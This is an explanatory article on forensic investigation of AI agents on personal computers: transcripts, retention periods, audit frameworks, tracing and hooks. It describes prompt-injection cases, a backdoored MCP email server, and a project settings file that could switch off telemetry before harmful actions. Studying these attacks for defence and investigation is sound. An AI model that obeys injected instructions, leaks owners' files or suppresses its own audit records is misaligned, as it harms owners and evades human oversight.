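# Reconstructing what an AI agent did on a personal computer: logs, provenance and replay

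## The compromised agent and the questions an investigator must answer

An AI agent is a language model that works on a task by choosing an action, seeing the result and choosing again. On a personal computer, it can run commands, edit files, read mail and use websites with the permissions of the person who started it. If an outsider influences the agent through instructions hidden in a document or a malicious add-on, the owner may notice nothing. An investigator must then work out what the agent did and why, perhaps weeks later.

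Part of the investigation is ordinary digital forensics, such as finding which files changed and which connections left the machine. The rest is newer because the agent chooses its own steps, and its choices depend on the text it has read so far. In *Foundations for Investigations of Agentic AI Systems*, Gruber and Hilgert (2026) analyzed the open-source assistant OpenClaw and framed the central question as what the agent did, as opposed to what its user requested, knew or intended. On a computer without an agent, a command run under someone's account points to that person or to malware. On a computer with one, the agent may also have run the command, whether it was following the owner's instructions, misreading them, or following someone else's.

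### The agent loop

The model usually runs on the provider's servers. The agent program, which engineers often call a "harness", runs on the owner's computer, where it prepares the model's input and carries out the model's requests. *Unrolling the Codex agent loop* (Bolin, 2026) explains this cycle for Codex CLI, OpenAI's command-line agent program.

The program first assembles the context, the exact text and images that the model will receive for one response. For Codex, the context includes general instructions, a list of the available tools, a note on which folders the agent may write to and when it must ask permission, any standing instructions from the owner's files, the current folder, and finally the owner's request. The program sends all of this over the network to the provider's server, which puts the items in order, adds its own system message and runs the model.

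The model then produces either a message to the user or a tool call, which is a structured request such as "run this command in this folder". The model cannot access the disk itself, so the agent program executes the call on the owner's machine, appends the call and its output to the context, and sends the full context back to the provider. In Bolin's example, the tool call runs a command that prints a project's README file. The call and its output carry the same identifier, so anyone reading the record later can match them. A single turn may include hundreds of calls, but it always ends with a message to the user, such as "I added the architecture.md you asked for".

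The agent's actions mostly happen on the owner's machine, but the model chooses them at the provider. The provider sends back the response and, in Codex, a summary of the reasoning text (the intermediate text that a model produces before it answers or acts), along with an encrypted block that only the provider can open. When the context of a long session nears its size limit, the program replaces it with a shorter version, so the model may choose its last actions from a condensed form of what it read at the start.

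### How an agent comes to serve someone else

The model receives the owner's request, an invoice and a web page as parts of one long input. Codex labels messages with roles that carry different weight, but a model may still follow instructions in a file it was only supposed to read. Prompt injection means planting such instructions in material the agent will read.

Injected instructions do not always come from criminals. *Alibaba Cloud Got Caught Prompt-Injecting AI Agents* (The Hacker News, December 2026) reported that the Chinese cloud provider's official command-line tool had been returning error messages written for AI agents. The messages told agents to send back the computer's login name and public IP address, along with their current task and instructions. The company called this a countermeasure against suspected automated abuse and said it would stop. The developer who noticed the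 messages sent none of this information. There is no evidence that any agent complied, but the company has not said whether it received data, so customers whose agents used the tool that week can only check their own records.

Attackers can also compromise an agent through its add-ons. These include *skills*, which are packages of written guidance and sometimes code, and *MCP servers*, small programs that offer extra tools through a common standard, the Model Context Protocol. Bolin notes that Codex's sandbox covers only its own command tool, so MCP servers have to enforce their own limits. Checking an add-on before installation offers limited protection. *A fake AI agent skill passed every security scanner* (Constantin, 2026) reports that the security firm AIR got a harmless fake skill past scanners from Cisco and NVIDIA. AIR says the skill reached 26,000 agents. *Experts warn malicious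 AI skills are hitting more victims than ever* (TechRadar, August 2026) describes cloned skills that received credential-stealing code only later. One family had 1.7 million downloads, though that figure doesn't show how many users were harmed.

Many agents save notes to memory, and the agent program loads them into the context of later sessions. In *Auditable Agents*, Nian, Yuan and colleagues (2026) scanned OpenClaw and its skills and found a skill that told the agent to modify its long-term memory file. A compromised skill or an injected document could do the same to keep its instructions active across sessions. This complicates an investigation because the harmful act may come weeks after the text that caused it, in a session where no attack took place.

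None of these routes has to produce a visible symptom. The agent works under its owner's account and with its usual tools, so the computer records its activity as the owner reading their own files. *AI agent security* (Constantin, 2026) describes research by Manifold Security in which another browser extension could make Anthropic's Claude for Chrome read the owner's mail, documents and calendar. When the owner had turned on the "Act without asking" option, Claude did so silently.

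The agent's closing message is little help either. Dziemian, Lin and colleagues (2026), in *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?*, ran a public competition in which attackers had to make an agent do something harmful and, in nearly all scenarios, keep any hint of it out of the final reply. In one scenario, the user asks the agent to check for urgent mail, and a planted marketing email gets the agent to mark a message about a contract deadline as read and leave it out of the summary. Across 41 scenarios and 13 models, 464 participants made about 272,000 attempts, of which 8,648 succeeded. Attacks succeeded against every model, at rates from 0.5% for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro.

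Dziemian and colleagues call these percentages an upper bound because the participants saw the conversation in advance and knew exactly which tool call they had to provoke. The models also date from 2025. However, the rates are per attempt, and successes kept accumulating at a roughly steady pace as people tried more. An attacker who can mail one document to ten thousand people gets ten thousand attempts. Most agent programs show a history of tool calls, but it is long and tedious, and users tend to read only the final reply.

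### Two cases from real machines

In September 2025 a package named postmark-mcp appeared on npm, a public registry of JavaScript code. It was an MCP server that let agents send email. Postmark, the email service whose name the package borrowed, says that the impostor built trust over 15 versions and then added a backdoor that blind-copied users' emails to an outside server. Koi, the security firm that discovered the backdoor, found that the change was one line of code.

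It is unclear how many people were affected. Koi counted about 1,500 downloads a week and estimated that some 300 organisations were using the package, but that estimate assumes that 20% of installations were active. Koi also says the tool had become part of developers' daily work, but *Researchers Discover First Malicious MCP Server in Rogue Postmark-MCP Package* (ThaiCERT, 2025) gives dates that leave little time for this. The developer uploaded the package on 15 September and released the malicious version on 17 September.

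The model in this case worked correctly. It requested that an email be sent and received a success message. The add-on inserted the extra recipient inside its own code after the model made its request, so a transcript (the agent program's saved record of messages, tool calls and results) could show no sign of it. Koi told victims to search their email logs instead. The developer deleted the package from npm, which removed the public copy but left installed copies running.

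In a case from October 2026, by contrast, the tools were ordinary and the attack came through a text file. Forever Security's *Markdown Is the New Executable* describes how the firm's product stopped a coding agent on a customer's machine as it was about to install a package already known to be malicious. The agent was following an instruction file in the Downloads folder, of a kind that coding agents read on startup and obey. The file looked like engineering notes. Nobody at the customer had put it there, and nobody knew how it had arrived.

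Forever Security, which sells protection against such attacks, later showed that a web page could have delivered the file without a click. It did not establish that this happened on this particular machine. The investigators knew what the agent had tried to do and which text had prompted it, but they could not tell how the file had got there.

### An invented case: forty invoices

In this invented case, an owner asks an agent to file 40 invoices by reading each PDF and moving it to the right folder. One of the PDFs contains hidden instructions. After reading it, the agent follows those instructions and sends a tax return from another folder to an outside site. It then finishes the filing and accurately reports "40 invoices filed". The owner learns of the leak 21 days later.

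On day 21 the owner knows only that the tax return has leaked. An accountant, a stolen password or ordinary malware could explain the leak as easily as the agent, so an investigator must first find out whether the agent was involved. If it was, did anything else leave the machine? Which of the 40 documents caused the leak, or was the cause an old note in the agent's memory? Did the owner click "approve" without reading? And can the investigator trust records that have spent three weeks on a computer where the agent could write files?

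### Five conditions for a defensible verdict

Nian and colleagues try to say in general what an agent system must supply before anyone can answer such questions. They call this property auditability and derive it from the form of the answer. A complete audit verdict, they propose, has five parts:

V = (s, c, ν, r, σ)

Here s is the action under audit, c the circumstances in which it occurred, ν the finding that it complied with or violated a stated policy, r the responsible component or chain of components, and σ whatever protects the record against alteration. Each depends on a different property of the system.

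**Action recoverability** supplies s. Nian and colleagues measure it both as the share of relevant actions that appear in the record and as the average share of necessary details that survive for each recorded action. A log of the invoice session that lists every tool call by name and nothing else scores 100% on the first measure but close to zero on the second, because it would show an upload but neither the file nor the address.

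**Lifecycle coverage** supplies c. The record must include the phases of the run, including retries, refusals, approvals and handoffs to other agents. Suppose an agent sends an email after a policy check has blocked its first version. If the record omits the blocked attempt, an auditor cannot tell whether the email was a clean action or a successful workaround. The percentage of phases recorded can mislead, because a missing tenth may be one step or a thousand, so a second measure counts how much is missing. One problem remains unsolved. Unless the program marks the start and end of each phase, a phase that never happened looks the same as one that nobody recorded.

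**Policy checkability** (ν) is the share of policies that a mechanical check can settle from the record. The policies must be structural, such as "tool X requires prior approval from the user". The framework excludes a rule like "do only what the owner would want", although this is the rule the owner cares about most in a silent compromise.

**Responsibility attribution** supplies r by tracing an action from the component that executed it back to the person or system that set it in motion. This is fairly clear for delegated work but less so for injected instructions. In the invoice case, one chain runs from the upload through the agent to the owner, who started the task, and another runs to whoever wrote the PDF. Tracing the second chain requires a record of what the agent read and what that text led to. Goli (2026) argues in *Five Questions Security Teams Must Be Able to Answer* that, without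 such provenance, investigators at companies may reconstruct an action and still not know reliably what influenced it. Attribution is even harder when agents use their user's credentials, because the action is then recorded under the user's name.

**Evidence integrity** supplies σ, and the other four depend on it. Nian and colleagues grade it on a four-level scale, from no protection to digital signatures that an outsider can verify.

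They define a run as auditable if it reaches set thresholds on these measures for a given list of policies, but they offer no guidance on setting the thresholds. Their argument that five conditions are enough is informal. Their supporting experiments all use tools they built themselves, and they have not yet fully audited any deployed system. The framework is most useful as a checklist of ways a record can fail.

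### One missing field

The most practical result in *Auditable Agents* concerns checking a policy against a record. The check can return "comply", "violate" or "undecidable" (written ⊥). "Undecidable" here means that the record lacks the information needed to decide, which is unrelated to undecidability in mathematical logic.

Let F be the set of fields that a policy requires, and S the set of steps in the run whose records could bear on it. If a field in F is absent from the records of every step in S, the result is ⊥, because a decision requires every field in F to appear somewhere in those records. Nian and colleagues concede that this is not deep, and it follows almost directly from how they define a decision. It matters because the designer of a log format chooses the fields long before any incident.

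Suppose that in the invoice case the agent program logs four things for each tool call: the time, the tool, the file and the destination. The owner's rule is that any upload to an outside site needs prior approval. The log shows that the tax return was uploaded and gives the site's address, but it has no field for approvals. It would be the same whether the owner clicked through a prompt or no prompt appeared. Logging more events with the same four fields would not settle which happened, because the log would still lack a record of approvals.

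Suppose a different rule allows the agent to read only files in the invoice folder. The same four fields are enough to decide whether the agent broke this rule, and it did. Whether a question is undecidable therefore depends on both the rule and the record. An investigator can sometimes resolve an undecidable question by adding evidence to the record, for instance if another program on the machine happened to save the approval prompts.

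### Auditing, monitoring and prevention

Prevention would have stopped the upload, and live monitoring would have raised an alarm during it. Both can limit the damage, but an audit on day 21 is too late to do so. Goli describes two incidents that show the difference in time. When an agent misbehaved during a test at the UK AI Security Institute, monitoring detected unusual outgoing data and staff contained the incident within an hour. When an OpenAI agent accessed non-public files on an Australian government portal on 18 June 2026, the responsible agency did not learn of it until 10 September.

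But neither one replaces an audit. After an upload is blocked, an investigator still has to find out which document contained the instruction to make it, and whether the agent had already followed other instructions in that document. A filter also lets through actions that look normal, as nearly all do in a silent compromise. Nian and colleagues similarly distinguish auditability from *observability*, the engineers' term for dashboards and traces that show a system at work. With observability alone, an operator may see that a tool ran but be unable to show who approved it, or that nobody has edited the log entry since.

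The same software often serves several of these purposes. A program that intercepts each tool call to allow or refuse it is also well placed to record the call, the decision and the reason. Recording them at the time matters because later analysis can use only what survives. If no program recorded a field and it left no trace elsewhere, nobody can recover it on day 21.

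## What agent programs leave on the disk

On day 21, an investigator can start with the agent program's own files. The best-known agent programs keep detailed transcripts so that users can return to earlier work. Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, saves each session continuously, and the user can resume it after closing the program. The records needed to continue a conversation include much of what an investigator needs, but not all of it.

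### How Gruber and Hilgert examined OpenClaw

People run OpenClaw on their own computer or a rented server and instruct it through apps such as Telegram and WhatsApp. It can send email, manage a calendar, control a browser and run commands. Gruber and Hilgert believe theirs is the first forensic study of a personal AI assistant.

Gruber and Hilgert installed version 2026.2.2-3 of the program on a virtual machine running Debian Linux and read the source code to learn where it might store data. They then saved an image of the whole disk, performed one action and saved another image. The actions included installing the program, sending it text and voice messages, adding calendar events and starting sub-agents, which are temporary helpers that take over part of a task. A script compared each pair of images and listed every file that had appeared, disappeared, or changed its name, contents or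 timestamps. They filtered out the operating system's background activity, opened the remaining files and checked the contents against what they had typed.

This method links each file to the action that changed it, which is hard to do on a computer in ordinary use. However, Gruber and Hilgert studied only the disk, on one operating system, and did not examine working memory or network traffic. They also did not test how long the evidence lasts over long periods, so the deletion times they report describe the program's rules rather than losses they observed over weeks.

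### Five classes of artifact

The tested version stores nearly everything in a hidden folder named `.openclaw` in the user's home directory. Gruber and Hilgert sort the folder's contents into five classes, each useful for answering a different question about the agent.

| Class | Question | Main files in the tested version |
|---|---|---|
| Reasoning and cognition | How did the model reach its choices? | Reasoning text and changes of model, in the session transcripts |
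| Identity and configuration | What was the agent able to do? | `openclaw.json` and its backups, persona files such as `SOUL.md`, skills, credentials |
| Knowledge and recall | What did the agent know? | `MEMORY.md`, daily memory logs, `USER.md`, a searchable index of memories |
| Communication | Who gave the agent messages, and what could they see? | Messages in the transcripts, received files in `media/inbound/`, channel settings |
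| Actions and effects | What did the agent do? | Tool calls and results in the transcripts, records of scheduled tasks in `cron/`, a register of sub-agents |

The transcripts are the richest source and contribute to every class. Each is a JSONL file, in which every line is a separate structured record.

In the invoice case, the configuration would show whether the agent had permission to run the upload. The memory files might contain a note planted earlier. The records of scheduled tasks would help identify actions that did not follow a request from the owner.

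The communication class also covers the difference between what happened and what the owner saw. With models that mark their reasoning with tags, such as Google's Gemini, OpenClaw forwards only the final text to the chat app. So the transcript on the disk can contain the whole upload while the owner's Telegram shows only "40 invoices filed".

When the main agent delegates a task to a sub-agent, the sub-agent's transcript stores the instruction as a message from the "user". Someone who opened only that file would mistake the instruction for a request from the owner. To see who gave it, an investigator has to look in the parent session for the call that started the sub-agent.

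Gruber and Hilgert checked their five classes against two published inventories, one by Walker and colleagues for Microsoft's agent framework AutoGen and one by Dragonas and colleagues for the ChatGPT mobile app. Every AI-specific item fitted one of the classes, but this is weak support because the classes are broad and Gruber and Hilgert did not examine either system themselves. The comparison also showed that the AutoGen inventory had nothing under reasoning or actions. This was partly because AutoGen had abandoned its runtime logging and partly because Walker's team had not considered those kinds of evidence, an oversight that a checklist makes less likely.

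### One tool call in a transcript

Suppose the owner of the 40 invoices used this version of OpenClaw. The session's transcript opens with a header that contains the session's identifier, creation time and working folder. Each later line contains its own identifier and its parent line's identifier, so an investigator can rebuild the sequence.

Partway through, the agent reads the seventeenth invoice with a tool call, and the result contains the extracted text, including the hidden instructions. The agent's next message contains a call to `exec`, a tool that runs shell commands. This call has a unique identifier, and its arguments contain the full command, including the path of the tax return and the address of the outside site.

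OpenClaw runs the command and adds a result to the transcript. As in Codex, the result repeats the call's identifier. It also contains the command's output, the time and an `isError` flag, which is false here. For shell commands, OpenClaw may add how long the command ran and its exit code, a number that indicates success or failure.

This pair of records shows which file the agent sent and where, but it does not prove that the outside site accepted the file. An error flag of "false" means only that the tool reported no error. The tool's code may also have done more than its arguments show, as in the postmark-mcp case. Gruber and Hilgert mention no field in these records for the owner's approval.

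The transcript also keeps the file contents that the agent reads, writes or edits through its file tools. An investigator can therefore recover the text of the seventeenth invoice even if someone has since deleted the PDF, and can follow how the agent changed its own memory files. The transcript does not include edits that the owner made in another program.

### What the tested version loses

The largest gap is the context, which the tested version did not save. The transcript supplies most of the conversation. A report in the session index sometimes lists which memory and instruction files went into the context, but it can be missing or reflect only the latest state. It also omits the full tool descriptions. These descriptions matter because a malicious add-on can use them to give the model instructions that never appear in the conversation.

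Like Codex, OpenClaw condenses the context of a long session. The transcript marks where this happened. After that point, the model received less information than the original messages contain.

OpenClaw also writes runtime logs outside its main folder, in `/tmp/openclaw/`. They record the start and end of each tool call and often list the tools available for a run. Gruber and Hilgert point out that a call recorded in these logs but missing from the transcript suggests that someone has tampered with the transcript. But OpenClaw deletes logs older than 24 hours when it starts up, so by day 21 this comparison is no longer possible. Restarting the program to examine it can also destroy the logs.

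OpenClaw keeps entries in its register of sub-agents for even less time. Depending on the settings, it removes an entry as soon as the sub-agent finishes or keeps it until a deadline, by default 60 minutes after creation. The sub-agent's transcript often remains on the disk, and the parent's transcript contains the call that started the sub-agent.

When a user deletes a session, the tested version removes it from the index but leaves the transcript on disk, adding `.deleted` and the time to its name. It also keeps old copies of its configuration, each with the date of its last change. An investigator could estimate which permissions applied during the invoice session from the latest copy that predates it. Comparing successive copies shows what changed, such as a newly added chat channel.

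### What has changed since the study

OpenClaw has since moved most of these records. According to its *Session state on disk*, it now keeps the session index and transcripts in a single-file SQLite database for each agent. The JSONL transcripts and the old index file are leftovers from earlier versions. An investigator who follows the study's file paths on a current installation may find only old sessions, or none. Nous Research's *Session Storage* describes the same change in its assistant, Hermes Agent.

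A database also needs more careful copying. SQLite writes changes, including deletions, to a companion file whose name ends in `-wal` before it merges them into the main file, so copying only the main file can miss the latest activity. Upgraded installations may hold a second copy of older sessions, because the migration keeps the original transcripts in an archive folder with no automatic expiry.

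The most important change concerns the context. OpenClaw's *Trajectory bundles* describes a "flight recorder" that is on by default and stores the prompt, the system prompt and the tool definitions sent to the model, along with tool calls and results. This overtakes the study's finding that the context is not saved, but only for a while and within limits:

- Each session keeps at most 10 MiB of these events, and the oldest make way for new ones.
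- OpenClaw removes runs older than 14 days, and older runs sooner if the total exceeds 512 MiB.
- It cuts off text longer than 65,536 characters or so, and marks the cut.
- A crash can destroy events that the program has not yet written to the database.

In the invoice case, if OpenClaw had kept running, its hourly cleanup would normally have removed the context about a week before the owner learned of the leak, but the transcript would still be there. If the owner had found out on day 10, an investigator could probably have read both.

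OpenClaw has a command to export the recording, but the export leaves out image data, credentials and local paths. It is suitable for a support request, but the database itself is a better source for an investigation, particularly if the hidden instructions were in an image.

Ordinary transcripts now last much longer than the recording. According to OpenClaw's *Store maintenance and retention*, the program archives ordinary sessions after 30 days without activity, which hides them from the main list but leaves the transcript in the database. When a user deletes a session, OpenClaw keeps a compressed copy, by default with no age limit. If an agent exceeds its disk budget of 10 GB, the program starts removing the oldest deleted sessions. Separate sessions for scheduled tasks leave the live store after 24 hours, and the list of completed runs goes back seven days. A planted instruction carried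 out in a scheduled task would therefore leave less of a record than one carried out in the main chat.

OpenClaw's runtime logs disappear after 24 hours, according to its *Logging*. Its *Database layout* lists approvals among the contents of a separate database that all agents share. To establish what the owner consented to, an investigator would have to check whether the entries for the day in question include individual decisions or only standing permissions.

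### Claude Code

Claude Code writes a plain-text JSONL transcript for each session. According to Anthropic, the transcript records everything that passes through a tool, including file contents and command output. It can also contain the system prompt, the tool definitions and the instruction files that Claude Code loaded, so it may preserve much of the model's context. *AI Agents X Digital Forensics 03*, by the French security firm Intrinsec, lists other useful fields, such as the model that answered, the working folder and the message each record responds to. A separate file, `history.jsonl`, contains only what the user typed.

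Agent programs can leave a lot of data on the disk. In a test described in *Lab Notes* (2026), a forensic practitioner's blog post, Claude Code ran 97 commands in response to one simple request. Willison (2025), a software developer, had accumulated 379 MB of transcripts.

By default, Claude Code deletes transcripts older than 30 days. On day 21, the transcript of the invoice session would have nine days left. Claude Code deletes old transcripts during normal use, so an owner who notices the leak but keeps working may lose the transcript before anyone copies it. Users can set a longer period, and Willison suggests 99,999 days, or about 274 years.

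The agent's memory notes are exempt from this deletion, so after a month an investigator may find a planted note in the memory folder but no trace of the session in which the agent wrote it.

### Codex, OpenCode and Cursor

Codex also writes one JSONL file per session. The file name contains the start time and part of a session identifier that OpenAI's servers generate (Vaughan, 2026, *Codex CLI Rollout Files*). That identifier could help match the local file with any records OpenAI holds. According to Intrinsec's *AI Agents X Digital Forensics 02*, the file contains the user's messages, the agent's replies and, after each reply, a count of the tokens (pieces of text) processed. When a user archives a session, Codex keeps the full file (Vaughan, 2026, *Codex CLI Session Lifecycle*). Codex can also report whether a user or a setting approved each tool call, but only through an export that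 is off by default (OpenAI, *Advanced Configuration*).

The open-source coding agent OpenCode uses an SQLite database. Intrinsec's *AI Agents X Digital Forensics 01* describes one table of sessions, with titles, times, models and token counts, and another of messages. The session table also has a field for a sharing link, which is worth checking early in a leak investigation because information can leave the machine through a shared session. Text entries in the message table come from the model if they contain start and end times, and from the user if they don't. An investigator who overlooked this could attribute the agent's words to the user.

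Cursor, a code editor with a built-in agent, stores its records in several places. *Blacklight* (Kramer, 2026) catalogues the files of four agent programs as of July 2026. For Cursor, it includes chat databases, prompt history, plans, snapshots and a database that tracks AI-written code. Kramer's software can recover session titles, times and messages from the chat databases.

All of these records depend on the program's settings. Codex's `--ephemeral` option stops it from writing session files, and Claude Code has a similar option, so an empty folder doesn't prove that an agent was idle.

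### Desktop and browser agents

Less is documented about what agents outside the terminal and the code editor leave on the disk. The best documented are Claude Desktop and Cowork, Anthropic's agent for general office work. Since version 2.1.248, Claude Code has kept transcripts of sessions that a user started or last continued in either of them indefinitely, instead of applying its 30-day limit, unless the user or an organisation sets a limit. If the discovery had taken two months, the invoice owner would therefore be more likely to still have a transcript from Cowork than from Claude Code in a terminal.

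IRFlow's *AI Artifacts*, the documentation for the forensic timeline tool, describes Claude Desktop's own files as metadata that link to Claude Code transcripts. The transcripts are in a different folder, so someone who copied only the desktop app's folder would get the links without the conversations.

IRFlow also covers the ChatGPT desktop app and Atlas, OpenAI's web browser, but only if conversation data exists locally. IRFlow's *AI Query History and AI App Artifacts* lists the folders to check. If they are empty, the investigator depends on the owner's online account or the provider. A browser agent may therefore leave a much poorer local record than a coding agent, even though it can reach the owner's mail and documents.

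The table gives the main location for each program, with `~` standing for the user's home folder.

| Program | Main session record | How long it lasts by default |
|---|---|---|
| OpenClaw | `~/.openclaw/agents/<agentId>/agent/openclaw-agent.sqlite` | Ordinary sessions beyond 30 days, within a 10 GB budget |
| Claude Code | `~/.claude/projects/<project>/<session>.jsonl` | 30 days |
| Claude Desktop and Cowork | Claude Code transcripts, plus linking files in the app's folder | No age limit |
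| Codex | Dated folders in `~/.codex/sessions/` | Intrinsec gives no period |
| OpenCode | `~/.local/share/opencode/opencode.db` | Intrinsec gives no period |
| Cursor | `store.db` files within `~/.cursor/chats/` | Kramer gives no period |

*Lab Notes* lists Claude Code's transcripts in an extra subfolder that does not appear in Anthropic's documentation, so searching the whole `.claude` folder is safer than relying on one path.

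### Tools that collect the records

Finding, copying and reading these files by hand is slow, and several free tools now do parts of the work. The most ambitious, AgentDFIR, detects which agent programs are on a computer, copies their files unaltered into a sealed package and builds a timeline. Its developers list parsers for 12 products, including Claude Code, Codex, Cursor, OpenClaw and OpenCode. It can also work from a disk image, so investigators don't have to start the suspect computer.

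Transcripts from a compromised agent may contain prompt injections, so AgentDFIR treats their text purely as data. It never runs the agent programs it finds, and it neutralises invisible characters that could mislead a person reading the output.

Its most useful idea is to label how well the evidence supports each action. "Requested" means that a person asked for the action, "reported" that the model claimed to have done it, and "observed" that the transcript contains a tool call. An action is "corroborated" when independent records from the computer or network confirm it, "contradicted" when they show that it did not happen, and otherwise "unknown". In the invoice case, the upload would count as observed based on the transcript alone. The "contradicted" label requires caution because an event may be missing from a system log only because the system was not logging that kind of event.

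AgentDFIR can also try to trace each line of an agent's instruction files to the session and tool that wrote it, and to determine whether a person's request or a tool's output prompted the change. An investigator would want to know this about a planted memory note. The tracing can work only while the relevant transcript exists, and Claude Code deletes transcripts after a month by default.

The project supplies synthetic incidents for testing and training, but it reports no error rates and no results from real cases. Its public GitHub page had six "stars", which are similar to bookmarks, and this suggests that few people were using it. An investigator should check the tool's important findings against the original files, which the sealed package makes possible.

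The "agentdfir" package on PyPI, the public registry of Python software, is a different program called AgentTrace. It analyses logs that other systems have recorded and does not collect files from agent programs. Its developers have tested it only on synthetic data.

Smaller tools have a narrower scope. Wolfert (2026) released ai-hist, which turns the local histories of coding assistants into a timeline of chats and commands. Gruber and Hilgert published a tool for OpenClaw that merges logs, transcripts and configuration changes into one timeline and looks for calls missing from the transcript. They found that it reduced manual work in their own analysis but give no measurements. They built it around the file formats of the OpenClaw version they tested.

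Kramer built Blacklight mainly for authorised security teams that simulate attacks and would want to steal the same files, though it also includes detection rules for defenders. Kramer ran it on two home computers and found that its count of Claude messages was too high because the software did not distinguish the agent's messages from those the person typed. Kramer has since corrected this, but in an investigation the error would make it hard to tell the owner's requests from the agent's own activity. Gruber and Hilgert's method could reveal such faults before a tool is used in a real case. A tester would perform known actions on a clean machine and count how many the tool recovers and attributes correctly.

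## Hooks and tracing tools

Unlike a transcript, a record made for auditing usually exists only if the owner or employer turned it on before the incident. *Tracing* exports timed records of the agent program's own work. *Hooks* make the program call an outside program, which can log the event, at set points such as just before the agent runs a command. Both kinds of record can be sent straight to another computer, where they can outlast the local transcripts and a compromised agent cannot easily edit them.

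### How a task becomes a tree of spans

A trace consists of records called spans. Each span covers one piece of work, such as a model call or a tool call. It has a start time, an end time and a pointer to the larger piece of work that contains it, so software can display the whole task as a tree.

Claude Code can export such traces. According to Anthropic, each prompt from the user starts a root span, and the model requests and tool calls that follow become its children. Each tool call has two children of its own, one for the wait for permission and one for the execution. Part of the invoice session would look like this:

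```
Interaction (the owner's request)
├─ Model request
├─ Tool call: read invoice 17
│  ├─ Wait for permission
│  └─ Execution
├─ Model request
├─ Tool call: shell command (the upload)
│  ├─ Wait for permission
│  └─ Execution
└─ Model request
```

The permission span helps establish whether the owner approved the upload, which is unclear from many logs. Its duration is also useful, because someone who approved a long command in half a second probably did not read it.

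The tree also makes delegation easier to follow, because the spans of a Claude Code sub-agent appear beneath the tool call that started it. This avoids the confusion that OpenClaw's separate sub-agent transcripts can cause.

However, the tree shows which task each action was part of, but not what caused the action. Reading invoice 17 and uploading the tax return are siblings under the same request. The agent read the invoice before the upload, so the invoice may have caused it, but so may any of the 16 invoices the agent had already read.

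### What the OpenTelemetry conventions define

Claude Code exports its data through OpenTelemetry, an open standard that lets monitoring tools from different vendors read the same records. OpenTelemetry also publishes conventions for the names and fields of generative AI spans. Its *Semantic Conventions for GenAI agent and framework spans* covers running an agent, and its *Semantic conventions for generative client AI spans* covers model calls and tools.

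| Span | Fields recorded where available | Fields recorded only if someone opts in |
|---|---|---|
| `invoke_agent` | Agent's name, identifier and version; conversation identifier; model; token counts; reason the model stopped | Messages sent to the model |
| `execute_tool` | Tool's name, type and description; identifier of the call; type of error | Arguments and result |

With these defaults, the trace of the invoice session would show when the agent ran a shell command and that no error occurred, but it would not contain the command, the file or the address.

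OpenTelemetry leaves out prompts and outputs by default because they are often sensitive and large. Developers can record them on spans, or store them separately and put only a reference on the span. The project recommends separate storage in production because it allows stricter access rules. As of the April 2026 text, the project planned to define a common format for those references but had not yet done so.

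One of the default fields, the tool's description, could reveal instructions that a malicious add-on had hidden there, but only if the agent calls the tool. The model reads the descriptions of all available tools, so a poisoned description can influence it even if the agent never calls that tool and no span is recorded.

The conventions are not final. OpenTelemetry's *Gen AI* notes that they have moved to a separate repository, and TrueFoundry, a company that sells AI infrastructure, reported in August 2026 that they still had the status "Development". Field names may therefore differ between products or between versions of the same product.

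### What Claude Code and Cowork export

Tracing in Claude Code is in beta and off by default. The user or an administrator has to turn it on with two settings and choose where to send the spans. Even then, Claude Code removes prompt text, tool call details and the content tools return, unless someone turns on a separate switch for each.

Anthropic lists several kinds of tool call whose returned content Claude Code does not record even with all three switches on, including calls that end in an error and file reads that return an image or a PDF. All 40 documents in the invoice case are PDFs, so if the agent opened them with its file-reading tool, the trace would show 40 reads but none of the text. The trace could include the text if the agent extracted it with a shell command, since the command's output could be recorded.

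Claude Code also cuts off each piece of content at 60 KB by default, roughly 15,000 tokens. It marks the cut and gives the original length. Hidden instructions at the end of a long document would be lost, but an investigator would know that text was missing.

A project folder can contain its own Claude Code settings. These cannot turn telemetry on or redirect it, but they can turn an export off unless an administrator's settings or the environment in which the user starts the program already set the exporter. An attacker who supplies a malicious project could include a settings file that stops the trace before the agent does anything harmful. Administrators can prevent this by setting both the exporter and the destination centrally.

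Cowork has a different export, which is available only on Team and Enterprise plans, according to Anthropic's *Monitoring*. An administrator enters the address of a collector, the server that receives the records, and Cowork sends it an event for each prompt, model request, error, tool result and permission decision. Events that follow from the same prompt share an identifier. The permission events give the source of each decision, such as a setting, a hook, or a temporary or permanent choice by the user. In the invoice case, this would show whether the owner approved only this upload or had approved all such commands months earlier.

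By default, these events contain only metadata. An administrator can add the prompts and the tools' arguments, but Cowork shortens any text in the arguments to 512 characters and the arguments as a whole to about 4,000. A long command could therefore lose its destination address.

Collection can also fail without an obvious warning. If an organisation restricts network access and its administrator forgets to allow the collector's address, the system silently drops the records. Sessions already open when the administrator changes the settings do not pick up the changes. Anthropic notes that neither Claude Code in the terminal nor the Code tab of the desktop app sends anything to a collector entered in the Cowork form, so a company could see events arriving and still have no exported record of its coding agents.

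The private owner of the 40 invoices is worse off, because the Cowork export requires a Team or Enterprise plan. Individuals can use Claude Code's export, but someone has to run a collector to receive it. Codex's export is also off by default.

### Recording every action with hooks: Elastic and Cursor

A hook doesn't depend on the vendor's export format, because the outside program controls what is recorded. Elastic's *13 million tool calls* describes one such log in detail. Elastic, which sells search and security software, had given Cursor's agent to hundreds of developers before realising it had no record of what the agent did on their laptops.

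Elastic's script runs at 13 points. These are the start and end of a session, before and after each shell command and each call to an MCP server, after any tool call succeeds or fails, before a file read, after a file edit, when a sub-agent starts or finishes, and when the agent loop ends. Each time, the following happens:

1. Cursor starts the script and passes it a structured description of the event.
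2. At four of the points, Cursor pauses the agent until the script replies "allow", "deny" or "ask". The script replies "allow" before it does anything else, so that a full disk or a bug cannot hold up the developer's work.
3. The script works out whether the agent is running in the editor, in the command-line program or remotely.
4. It adds one line to that day's log file.
5. Elastic's monitoring software, which was already on each laptop, sends the line to a central database.

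Each line gives the time, user, computer, session, model, event and tool, along with the command, file path or MCP server if there is one. It also has fields for the outcome and duration. Elastic decided not to log file contents, prompts or model responses. But each line includes a copy of Cursor's original description of the event, so anyone who adopts the script should check what it contains.

In the two months after its May 2026 rollout, the system logged over 13 million events from more than 1,100 machines. Staff can now find every machine on which an agent read a private key file last week, or list every command an agent ran on a given laptop. They can also look for commands that download a program and run it immediately.

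In the company's log, agents read files about four times as often as they ran shell commands, although staff had expected commands to be more common. Developers had connected their agents to more than 300 different MCP servers, 86% of which had only one or two users each. Before it had the log, the company knew only about the servers people remembered to mention. After an attack like postmark-mcp, a company with this kind of log could quickly find out who had used the malicious server.

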